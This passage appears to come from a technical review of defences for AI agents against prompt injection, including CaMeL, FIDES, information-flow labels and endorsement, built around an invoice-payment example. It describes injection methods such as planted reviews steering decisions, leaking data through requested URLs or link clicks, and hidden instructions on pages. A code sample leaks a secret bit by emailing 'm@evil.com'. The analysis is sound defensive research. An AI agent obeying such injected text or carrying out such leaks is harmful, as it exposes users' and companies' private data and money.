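CaMeL stopped almost every attack, but the agent completed far fewer tasks. The trade-off was worst in travel, where attacks had rarely worked anyway and CaMeL made the agent nearly useless. The remaining attack in travel may not be real. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) note in *The LLMbda Calculus* that one of the two successful attacks in CaMeL's original evaluation was a false alarm, because the agent had only quoted a hotel review and the benchmark counted the quotation as obeying the attack.

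Claude 3.5 Haiku is an old, small model, and CaMeL depends heavily on how well the privileged model plans. Nikolaou and colleagues ran CaMeL with Claude Haiku 4.5 on all 97 AgentDojo tasks, without attacks, and it completed 49. It failed another 22 because the planner's program didn't do what the user wanted, which a better planner might fix. It blocked at least 17 for breaking a policy, and a better planner would help with those only if it could find a permitted way to do the same task. *SecureClaw* (2026) also tested CaMeL's published code and found that none of 629 attacks succeeded, but the agent completed only 29 of the 97 tasks.

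Garby and colleagues separated the benefit of planning in advance from the benefit of the policies. They looked at 144 combinations of a task and an attack in AgentDojo's banking setting. In 97, the attack needed a tool or file that the user's task would never involve, so a fixed plan would normally defeat it without any policy. In the other 47, the plan already contained steps the attacker could exploit, such as a payment.

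The policies also roughly halved the number of banking runs CaMeL completed, to 18 of 48 with each of two models. The label checks in *SPA* (2026), a newer system that also plans first, had a similar effect across AgentDojo. None of 949 attacks succeeded with the checks, compared with four without them, but task completion fell from 53 to 29 percent.

This looks like a poor trade for a company using one of the newest models, several of which already resist nearly all of AgentDojo's standard attacks. The best argument for CaMeL is that its plan is fixed, so an attacker can't add a step by rewording the attack. That matters a lot for an agent that makes payments, since adaptive attacks have beaten many defences that looked good in fixed tests. Still, a low attack success rate alone is no reason to choose a system. Dongol (2026) points out in *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* that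 a monitor that denied every tool call would count as secure.

### When the next step depends on what the agent reads

A fixed plan works badly when nobody can know the next step in advance. Xiang and colleagues give the example of an agent that requests last week's sales from a billing service and learns that the service has moved to a new address. An ordinary agent would read the documentation and try again, while one with a fixed plan could only repeat the failed request. Debugging is even harder with a fixed plan, because each error message determines what to look at next.

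Only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan, according to Xiang and colleagues. CaMeL's AgentDojo results therefore probably overstate how well its design would do on work that often requires such changes, such as debugging.

The planner may lack information that even a simple plan needs. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) explains that the privileged model must write code to process a tool's output before seeing it, so the researchers had to add a description of the output format to every tool. Writing these descriptions is a small, one-time job for a company's own tools, but it is harder for an unfamiliar website.

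One response is to plan for many possibilities at once. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) does this for agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. The planner writes a program with branches for situations such as a cookie banner or a failed click, and a quarantined model identifies which one has occurred. The programs averaged 213 lines and 41 tool calls, compared with 52 lines and 5 tool calls for AgentDojo tasks.

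The test used 109 tasks that Claude Sonnet 4.5 could do without isolation. The isolated agent completed 28 percent of them on its first attempt and 57 percent within five attempts. That is impressive for a plan written without seeing the screen, but the first-attempt rate is the relevant one for payments, because a company can't safely let an agent try five times to pay a bill.

A flexible plan can also remove the protection it was meant to provide. In one banking task that Garby and colleagues ran, the user asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. CaMeL's planner wrote a loop with a branch for every tool, so whoever wrote the file could use any of them. With policies switched off, two attacks succeeded that a fixed plan should have stopped.

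Other designs let the agent read first and then check what it tries to do. In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026), the agent writes its actions as short Scala programs. A compiler rejects any program that could leak classified data or that uses a permission the agent lacks. The agent can change its plan after every step, and Odersky and colleagues found no significant loss in task performance. But an agent with permission to make payments could still pay the wrong account unless the payment tool also restricts the recipient.

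Li, Wang and colleagues (2026) take a similar approach in *PACE*. Their system works out permissions from the user's authenticated request and checks each tool call just before it runs. Across eight benchmarks, its task completion rate was at most three percentage points below that of an undefended agent, a much smaller drop than CaMeL's. However, the guarantee they proved for a stricter version doesn't fully cover the version they tested, because the tested version can restore calls that one of its checks has blocked.

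These systems avoid the drawbacks of a fixed plan by giving up its main benefit. Garby and colleagues point out that once an agent can write new steps after reading untrusted text, its security depends entirely on the checks. A policy then has to catch even the 97 attacks that a fixed plan would have made impossible.

*ActGuard* (2026) tries a compromise in which the agent predicts, at each step, which tools it will plausibly need next. The system compares the next action with that prediction but doesn't automatically block a mismatch. This leaves room for legitimate changes of plan, but it requires a judgment about whether each mismatch is acceptable, and an attacker might influence that judgment.

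### False data in a permitted field

A policy protects only the values it covers. Xiang and colleagues imagine a user who asks an agent to pay Joe back for a bouquet from a certain shop. The recipient passes CaMeL's check because the user specified him. But the agent has to look up the price, and a false price on a web page could make it pay Joe far too much.

Nikolaou and colleagues describe a stricter rule that requires both the recipient and the amount to come from trusted sources. The rule would stop the overpayment, but it would also stop an agent from paying any bill whose amount it had to read from an invoice. A company could instead accept the invoice's amount if it matched the purchase order.

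The answer to a yes-or-no question can be false too. In the program for Harlow Paper, planted reviews could make `sound` come out as yes. The company might then pay a supplier it should have avoided, even if the program took the account number from company records. A policy could refuse any payment that depended on web reviews, but then there would be little point in having the agent check them.

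Foerster and colleagues call this kind of attack branch steering, and they demonstrated it with an advertisement that looked like a cookie banner. The plan already contained a step for dismissing cookie banners, so the agent clicked on the advertisement and went to the attacker's site. Asking a second model to check the screen didn't reliably prevent this. The attacker could still only trigger steps already in the plan, which is a real improvement over an agent without that limit.

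Santos-Grueiro (2026) proposes tighter limits on such values in *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents*. Trusted code can approve a value from an untrusted document, but each approval covers only one named field. An invoice could then supply the payment reference without also setting the account or marking the payment as approved. The system doesn't guarantee that an approved value is correct, which depends on the code that validates it. *Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use* (2026) adds a check of this sort by comparing the quarantined model's answer with trusted evidence before accepting it. For an invoice, that could mean comparing its account number with the one the finance department has on file.

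No policy can fully solve the problem when the user asks the agent to make a payment based on a file's contents. Garby and colleagues built an agent that can deliberately accept untrusted data for a particular use, which is called endorsement. Attacks succeeded in only two of 1,296 runs, and in both the user had asked for a payment based on a file that the attacker had replaced. The four successful attacks on SPA also came from a banking task that involved acting on a file, and CaMeL's threat model excludes such cases. The agent is doing what the user asked, so the only remedies are to check the file's contents or refuse the request.

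### Writing policies and approving actions

Somebody also has to write the policies. Tallam and Miller warn that a large organisation may have hundreds of tools, each with its own rules, which can easily become inconsistent. A rule that is sensible for one task can also be wrong for another. Xiang and colleagues point out that if a user asked the agent to pay a bill sent from a certain email address, CaMeL's payment policy would block the payment because the account number would come from the email.

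Deriving permissions from each request, as Li and colleagues do, reduces the work. Nikolaou and colleagues instead check the whole program before it runs. If it breaks a rule, their system sends the privileged model a description of the problem, and the model writes a new program. For the invoice, the revised program might take the account from company records. The privileged model still hasn't read any untrusted text, so the extra attempt doesn't give an attacker a way in. Nikolaou and colleagues could check 22 of CaMeL's 28 AgentDojo policies in advance. The other six depended on facts available only while the program runs, such as who can read a shared file.

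When a policy blocks something legitimate, the usual solution is to ask the user to approve it. Willison predicted in 2023 that people would learn to click "OK" as fast as possible. He later cited a security expert who fell for a phishing email in 2025 as evidence that anyone can make this kind of mistake when tired. Tallam and Miller suggest asking only about riskier actions. Reading a calendar would need no approval, moving a file would need a quick confirmation if untrusted data was involved, and a bank transfer would need approval from more than one source.

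The user's approval should also be specific. Dongol describes an assistant that needs approval to send an email. If the approval covers any email, an injected instruction can use it to send private data before the assistant sends the reply the user had in mind. If it covers only the exact message and recipient, the attacker can't substitute another message. For a payment, the user should approve a specific account and amount, and the request should show whether the account matches the company's records. If the agent asks only when the account doesn't match, the user will see few enough requests to have a reasonable chance of reading them.

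## Labels that record where data came from and what it may affect

CaMeL blocks a payment if the account number came from a file, whether the user attached the file or the agent found it. A more general view is that an agent's trust in a text should depend on who could have influenced the text and what the agent is about to use it for, not on whether the agent chose it or was given it. Information-flow control is one way to build agents that follow this view. Each piece of data carries labels, and ordinary code checks them before an action goes ahead.

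### Two labels and a rule for combining them

The simplest scheme has two integrity labels. Data is trusted if no outsider could have influenced it, and untrusted otherwise. When an agent combines data, the result is untrusted if any of the inputs are. A sentence based on the user's request and a web page is therefore untrusted, even if nearly every word came from the user.

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, write the labels as T and U, and the operation that combines them, called a join, as ⊔:

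T ⊔ T = T

T ⊔ U = U

U ⊔ U = U

Security researchers call an ordered set of labels with such an operation a lattice, and it can have more than two levels. A label could instead list everyone who could have written the data, and the label on combined data would then list everyone who could have written any part of it. An account number from the company's records might have the label {finance staff}, and one from an invoice might have the label {the supplier, anyone who handled the file}.

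*Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) traces the idea to a 1977 model by K. J. Biba. Under the model's two rules, a program that reads untrusted data drops to that data's level of trust, and a program at that lower level can't authorise an important action.

Integrity labels are mainly useful for deciding what a text may affect, and an agent still has to judge for itself whether the text is true. If a finance clerk mistypes an account number, the company's records will contain a wrong number that is labeled trusted, even though the supplier's untrusted website may have the right one. Li, Mao and Zdancewic argue in *Information Integrity Policies* that integrity in this sense is weaker than what people need in practice.

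### The invoice task with labels

Suppose the user again types "Check that Harlow Paper is sound, then pay the attached invoice", and the agent keeps a single label for its whole context.

| What the agent does | Label of the choice | Label of the result | Label of the context afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reads the user's request | No choice | Trusted | Trusted |
| Searches the web for "Harlow Paper complaints" | Trusted | Untrusted | Untrusted |
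| Opens a link from the search results | Untrusted | Untrusted | Untrusted |
| Looks up Harlow Paper in the company's records | Untrusted | Untrusted | Untrusted |
| Tries to pay | Untrusted | Blocked | Untrusted |

Only the search was free of outside influence, because the agent had read text by strangers by the time it picked the link.

The fourth row is strict even though only finance staff can change the records, because in Costa's scheme a tool's result takes the combined label of the data the tool read and the request that led to it. For example, a planted review could claim that Harlow Paper now trades under another name, which belongs to a different supplier in the records. The agent would then find a genuine account number, but the stranger who wrote the review would have chosen which supplier got the money.

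If the agent looked up the account before searching the web, the number would stay trusted. The payment would still fail because the agent would decide to make it after reading the search results.

### FIDES

Costa and colleagues at Microsoft built an agent called FIDES that avoids this problem by keeping untrusted text out of the main model's context. Every message, tool argument and field of a tool result has a label. The system prompt, tool descriptions and user's messages are trusted by default. Anything the model writes gets the combined label of everything in its context, because nobody can tell which parts influenced the output.

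When a tool returns data that would make the context less trusted, FIDES stores that data in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. It hides only that data, so in a list of bank transactions the model might see the amounts and dates but only variable names in place of the memo lines, which a stranger can write. The model can pass a variable to another tool without reading its contents. If the model opens the variable, its context takes on the variable's label.

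As in the dual-LLM pattern, a quarantined model can answer questions about hidden text. The main model can restrict the answer to a yes or no, or to a short list of options, and FIDES records the restriction in the label, for example as "untrusted, yes or no". A developer can let a yes-or-no answer influence important actions, since one bit is too small to contain an instruction.

Before each tool call, ordinary code applies two kinds of policy. A consequential action, such as sending money, is allowed only if the decision to take it and its arguments are trusted. A developer can relax this for particular arguments, so a message might need a trusted recipient while its text can come from a web search. A call that sends information out is also allowed only if every recipient has permission to read it.

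FIDES could handle the invoice like this:

1. It reads the invoice and hides the contents in a variable.
2. It looks up Harlow Paper's account in the company's records. The context is still trusted, so the account number is too.
3. It searches for complaints and hides the results.
4. It asks the quarantined model whether the results suggest a sound supplier, and opens the yes-or-no answer.
5. It asks the quarantined model for the amount on the invoice and keeps the answer hidden.
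6. It requests a payment to the account from the records, for the hidden amount.

The payment goes through if the developer's policy allows the one-bit answer and an untrusted amount. FIDES chooses each step based on the trusted parts of earlier results, whereas CaMeL writes the whole plan in advance. This lets FIDES react to an error message from a trusted tool.

As with CaMeL, planted reviews could still make that one-bit answer wrong. An agent that opened 27 yes-or-no answers about a forged invoice could also reconstruct the forger's eight-digit account number, which contains about 27 bits. A policy therefore needs to limit how many such answers can influence an action.

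Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, using an attack written by someone who knows which tools the agent has. The basic agent in this table has labels but no hidden variables.

| Agent | Successful attacks | Office tasks completed | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic, no policy checks | 152 | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Basic, with policy checks | 0 | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
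| FIDES, no policy checks | 21 | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| FIDES, with policy checks | 0 | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

The completion rates are for runs without attacks. The policy checks alone stopped every attack, so the hidden variables weren't needed for security, but they let the agent complete more tasks under the same checks, about 50 percent on average across the four settings instead of 42. The basic agent completed 84 percent without checks. A stronger model, OpenAI's o1, reduced the loss, and with it FIDES completed 68 percent of the travel tasks with the checks on.

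The zeros exclude a few cases that AgentDojo had counted as successes, including attacks that changed the text of an answer without causing a forbidden action. Costa and colleagues also labelled as untrusted every field that any AgentDojo attack uses. A company can't do that, because it doesn't know in advance which fields an attacker will use.

One banking task shows how easily a label can be wrong. The user asked the agent to change a password if it saw a suspicious transaction, and the agent changed it after seeing a large amount. Amounts were labeled trusted because no attack in the benchmark alters them. But whoever sends a transfer chooses its amount, so if the transaction was incoming, a stranger could have triggered the password change.

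### Whether choosing a source can count as endorsement

An agent sometimes has to endorse untrusted data, which means deliberately accepting it for a particular use. Otherwise, it could never pay a new supplier. Choosing a source carefully might seem to count as endorsing its data.

Research on leaks of secret data suggests a test. In 2001, Steve Zdancewic and Andrew Myers introduced robust declassification, the principle that attackers shouldn't be able to affect what secret information a system releases or whether it releases any. Myers, Sabelfeld and Zdancewic, in *Enforcing Robust Declassification and Qualified Robustness*, illustrate it with a program much like this one:

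```
if x:
    y = declassify(z)
```

The program releases the secret `z` if `x` is true. An attacker who can change `x` controls whether the release happens, and one who can copy a different secret into `z` controls what comes out. The release is robust only if an attacker can do neither.

The same idea works for endorsement, with one difference. An outsider may have written the data, since otherwise nobody would need to endorse it. What the outsider mustn't influence is the decision to endorse. This program fails the test, because a forger can make a website look official:

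```
if site_looks_official:
    account = endorse(website.account)
```

*Nonmalleable Information Flow Control* (Cecchetti, Myers and Arden, 2017) builds this requirement into a small programming language. The language rejects any program in which untrusted data could affect whether the program endorses data (marks it as trusted).

The agent's first search meets the requirement, since the agent chose it before reading anything by a stranger. Its choice of link doesn't, because the search results influenced it. But meeting the requirement doesn't make an endorsement wise. A program could decide in advance to endorse every page it opens, and no attacker would have influenced that decision. The agent also needs a reason to trust whoever wrote the page.

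The agent can safely treat content as trusted for a particular use if, for that use, the company accepts the word of everyone who could have written the content at its source. The agent's information about who those writers are and whose word the company accepts must also be trusted. Only the finance staff could have written the company's payment records, and the company accepts their word for account numbers. An open web search can return content from anyone who can publish online.

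Before an agent reads untrusted text, it can safely choose a source, but that choice raises the content's label only if it is based on trusted knowledge of who can write to the source. That knowledge would justify the same label if a program had inserted the content without the agent choosing it. After reading untrusted text, the agent can't raise a label by its own choice, but it can ask the user or rely on a rule the company set beforehand.

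### A domain the user names

A harder case arises when a user types, "Harlow Paper's website is the one on our contract. Use the account number there", and gives the domain. The agent got the domain from the user, who is a principal, rather than directly from a stranger. If the user took it from the contract, no stranger influenced the choice of site. But if the user copied it from the invoice, the forger may have chosen the site.

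The domain identifies the site's owner but not who can write on each page. A supplier's site may have customer reviews, a page run by a marketing agency, or a link that redirects to another company. *The Devil is in the Context*, a 2026 classification of prompt injection attacks, similarly warns that when a system's policy marks a source as trusted, such as emails from internal senders, that label neither guarantees harmless content nor authorises every instruction in it.

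The label should therefore cover only what the user's knowledge supports. The agent could treat a page that only Harlow Paper's staff can edit as a statement from Harlow Paper, which is reliable enough for its opening hours or the price of a box of paper. It should label the site's review section like any other public text, and stop applying the user's endorsement if it follows a link to another domain.

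The user named the site and also explicitly approved a use for the account number. If the company lets this user decide where money goes, the agent can follow the instruction. If the company also requires finance to confirm new accounts, the user can't waive that requirement by naming a website. The agent should still tell the user that the number differs from the one on the invoice, because the user may not have known this when giving the instruction.

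An endorsement can also go wrong when the agent supplies the secret that the check relies on. Suppose the company keeps a secret passphrase for each supplier and lets anyone who knows it change the supplier's account. In a forged email, an attacker leaves the passphrase blank and asks the agent to fill it in from the supplier's file. A helpful agent does so, the check succeeds, and the company accepts the new account from someone who never knew the passphrase.

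Cecchetti and colleagues describe the same fault in a password checker, where carelessly written code passes in the real password as the visitor's guess. Their remedy, transparent endorsement, raises the trust level of information only if the people who supplied it could have read it. The forger couldn't have read the passphrase, so the agent shouldn't treat it as the forger's answer.

### Fetching a page sends a message

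When an agent opens a web page, whoever runs the site can read the address the agent requested. Willison uses the term "lethal trifecta" for the combination of private data, untrusted content and a way to communicate externally, because an attacker can use the untrusted content to make the agent send out the private data. He points out that any tool that can make a web request provides that way to communicate, even if it only loads an image.

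For example, a page could tell the agent to check Harlow Paper's credit rating at an address that ends with the company's bank balance. The agent would treat this as retrieving a source, but the request would send the attacker the balance even if the page were empty. Choosing to retrieve a page can therefore do damage before the agent reads it.

Confidentiality labels deal with this by listing who may read each piece of data. When an agent combines two documents, only people allowed to read both may read the result. A policy can then allow a web request only if its address and search terms contain nothing private. Costa and colleagues treat the user's messages as public, which is convenient for a benchmark but often wrong in practice, since even a search for "Harlow Paper complaints" reveals that somebody is looking into Harlow Paper.

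Integrity and confidentiality can require an agent to take the same steps in opposite orders. The agent should read the company's records before searching the web to keep the account number trusted, but search first to keep private data out of the search. If a single label covers the whole context, either order causes one of the two policies to block something. Hidden variables can solve this by letting the agent hold the account number without its main model reading it. In the AgentDojo tests, however, FIDES hid data only to protect integrity.

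A developer could also allow the agent to open only addresses that the user typed or that appeared in earlier results, so that it can't leak a secret by writing it into a new address. This helps a lot but doesn't prevent every leak. An attacker's page could offer ten links, one for each digit, and tell the agent to click them in the order that spells out an account number. Eight clicks would reveal eight digits, and the rule would allow every one because the links appeared on the page.

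*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) shows why it is risky to let the model decide what is private. In one attack, an outsider asks an agent to clean up a list that mixes real and invented facts about somebody. The agent deletes the invented ones, which reveals the real ones. This attack and two others obtained 43.8 to 75.6 percent of the protected items from an agent whose prompt set out a strict consent procedure. Earlier attacks had obtained no more than 3 percent.

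Their own system labels records by where they came from and uses code outside the agent's context to check every outgoing write or share. It reduced leaks to between 0 and 3.3 percent across eight attacks, and the agent completed 72.4 percent of harmless tasks, compared with 75.9 percent for the best alternative. The system still uses a separate model to judge whether a proposed message reveals a protected record, and the tests didn't cover prompt injection.

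### Labels that spread too far

The most common complaint about labels is that they spread until the agent can hardly do anything. If the whole context has a single label, one untrusted sentence makes everything after it untrusted. In the AgentDojo results, turning on the policy checks reduced the basic agent's completion of Slack tasks from 93 to 20 percent.

Some of this comes from careless steps. In one Slack task, FIDES listed all the channels even though the user had named the one to use. This made its context untrusted for no benefit. Better models make fewer such mistakes. Labelling each field separately also helps. Costa and colleagues also mention research on finding which messages influenced an answer and regenerating the answer from those alone.

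Other failures are harder to avoid. In about 44 percent of the banking tasks and 43 percent of the Slack tasks, the right next step depends on what the agent reads. If a user asks an agent to read a file and follow its instructions, the labels block most of the resulting actions, as intended. As with CaMeL, someone has to check the file's contents, or the agent has to refuse the task.

### Influence that survives paraphrase

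Another worry is that influence can pass through a model without leaving any recognisable text behind. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and Tang, 2026) distinguishes three ways this happens. An agent can paraphrase a stranger's text, call a different tool because of it without copying any of it, or store it in memory and use it days later.

Cai and colleagues built NeuroTaint, which examines the record of a finished task for signs that untrusted content influenced the agent. It looks for similar meaning as well as similar wording, and it tracks sources across sessions. If it finds no copied content, it replaces the suspicious text with something neutral and tests whether the agent would still have made the same tool call. On 400 scenarios that the researchers wrote, NeuroTaint scored 0.93 on a measure that combines missed cases and false alarms, where 1 is perfect, while their version of FIDES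 scored 0.52.

This result is weaker evidence against FIDES than it appears. Paraphrasing defeats a program that searches for matching words, but FIDES labels everything the model writes after reading untrusted text, whatever the wording. The same rule should cover a change of tool, because tool calls also get the context's label. Cai and colleagues say their comparison system reasons over labels and known paths between tools, which may explain why it missed those cases.

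They are right that FIDES can't distinguish harmful from harmless influence. An agent that reads ten harmless pages and writes a report gets the same label as one that a page has hijacked. They are also right about memory, since labels can protect later sessions only if the system stores them with its notes.

NeuroTaint works only after the task ends, so it could help a company find out why an agent paid the wrong account but couldn't stop the payment. Systems that match text while the agent is running have trouble with paraphrase. Li and colleagues check outgoing calls for protected data in various encodings. They acknowledge that paraphrased, translated or fragmented data can get past the check.

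### What a proof about labels covers

Labels can also be wrong because the code that tracks them has gaps. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found two in CaMeL. A program like this one can get a secret past its checks:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
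```

If the balance is above the threshold, `tmp` becomes false and gets a secret label. The program then skips the line that would change `rich`, so `rich` stays true and keeps its public label. The email goes out and reveals that the balance is high, although the labels show no violation. CaMeL labels a variable when the program changes it, but here the secret affects `rich` by leaving it unchanged.

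The other gap is that the ordinary code around CaMeL's interpreter tries again when a program fails. Whether a policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit of it. An attacker who can trigger enough attempts can extract the whole secret.

FIDES deliberately leaves some gaps. It stops an agent from copying a secret into a public message, but not from revealing information through the order of its tool calls. Garby and colleagues call such choices defensible but hard to audit, because nobody can tell on a particular run whether a short answer that got through was an intended exception or a leak.

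Their alternative, the LLMbda calculus, is a small programming language for agents in which every value has a label and every operation passes it on. They proved a version of noninterference for all programs in the language, including agents that write and run their own code. Noninterference means, roughly, that changing untrusted inputs can't change trusted outputs, and changing secrets can't change public outputs. The theorem applies directly to the program that runs the agent, and a computer has checked the proof.

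An agent written in this language can make exceptions only through an explicit `endorse` command, which an auditor can search for. Garby and colleagues also proved that endorsing data as trustworthy doesn't weaken the protection of secrets. A payment agent could therefore endorse the amount on an invoice without becoming more likely to leak the company's bank balance.

The theorem compares only runs that finish, so an attacker may still learn something from whether a run finishes. It also doesn't check the first label on each piece of data, so if somebody labels a forged invoice as trusted, the agent will treat it as trusted throughout.

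### Attackers who know about the labels

Most tests of these systems use fixed attacks. The defences that Nasr and colleagues broke were originally tested the same way, and Narisetty and colleagues warn that the results for these systems could be just as misleading.

Progent checks each tool call against a list of permissions, which a model updates as the agent works. To get the model to permit a malicious action, researchers wrote an attack that presented the action as a routine, already approved step. Without Progent, ordinary attacks against a small Qwen model succeeded 25.8 percent of the time. With Progent, they succeeded 4.2 percent of the time, and the attack designed for Progent succeeded 2.6 percent of the time.

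That is encouraging but limited evidence. The gentler wording may have made the agent less likely to obey in the first place, and Narisetty and colleagues tried only one such attack on one weak model. Progent doesn't track where data came from, so we can learn little about labels from this test. Li and colleagues, whose system does use provenance, report that a small adaptive search failed on all 30 of its targets, but with so few targets, the search's true success rate could be close to 10 percent.

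An attacker who can't get past the checks would probably attack the labels instead. Pasted text is an obvious target, since FIDES and CaMeL both trust the user's messages by default. Another is data left unlabeled by mistake, which the deployed form of FIDES treats as trusted, according to Narisetty and colleagues. Treating it as untrusted would be safer but would make labels spread even further.

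The attacker could also rely on the user to repeat untrusted data. FIDES doesn't normally restrict what the agent tells the user, so the agent can report that the supplier's website gives a certain account number. If the user then types "fine, pay that one" and repeats the number, it counts as trusted input. The user may have checked the number, or may have assumed that the agent had. An agent could reduce this risk by showing the source next to the number and remembering that it had seen the same number in an untrusted place.

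### Sources caught giving instructions

Suppose the agent notices hidden text on the supplier's website telling AI agents to skip all checks, and ignores the instruction. Xiang and colleagues ask whether the agent should still use the rest of the page, such as the account number. They answer "Probably not in many settings", but consider the question unresolved.

The two integrity labels don't help here, because the page is untrusted both before and after the agent finds the instruction. But the agent should now believe the page less, and how much less depends on how often honest pages contain such text. Suppose the agent was 90 percent sure that the website was genuine, and that 1 percent of fraudulent sites contain hidden instructions. Khodayari and colleagues found such instructions on about one page in 120,000. If that were the rate for honest sites, the probability that this one is genuine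 would fall below 1 percent. If their search missed most of the instructions and the true rate were one in 1,000, the probability would fall only to about 47 percent, but even that is far too low to justify paying an invoice.

The location of the instruction also matters. If it was in a customer's comment, the agent has learned something about that customer and very little about Harlow Paper. If it was in the main text, either Harlow Paper wrote it or somebody else can edit the page, and either way the agent has reason to doubt the account number. The agent may therefore learn that W, the group of possible writers in the earlier condition, is larger than it thought. Any endorsement that relied on the smaller group should then lapse, including for values the agent has already taken from the site. The agent can find those values only if it has recorded where each one came from.

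If agents abandoned every site containing an injection, a competitor could make them ignore all of Harlow Paper's site by posting a hidden instruction in its review section. It is better to discard only what the suspected author could have written.

An agent has to notice the instruction and report it before it can do any of this, and models often fail to do so even when they don't obey the instruction. Xiang and colleagues propose training models to state which instructions they intend to follow, so that a separate program can trace each one to its source and decide how to handle it. They also suggest that the agent predict, before opening a source, whether it should contain instructions. For example, the agent would expect instructions in an installation guide but not in a page of reviews.

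In that proposal, the agent's choice of source is useful because the agent has a purpose before the page can influence it, and can compare what it finds with what it was looking for. For example, an agent that went to Harlow Paper's website for an account number has no reason to expect advice about skipping checks. The agent could make the same comparison for an attachment if it wrote down what it expected before reading the file.
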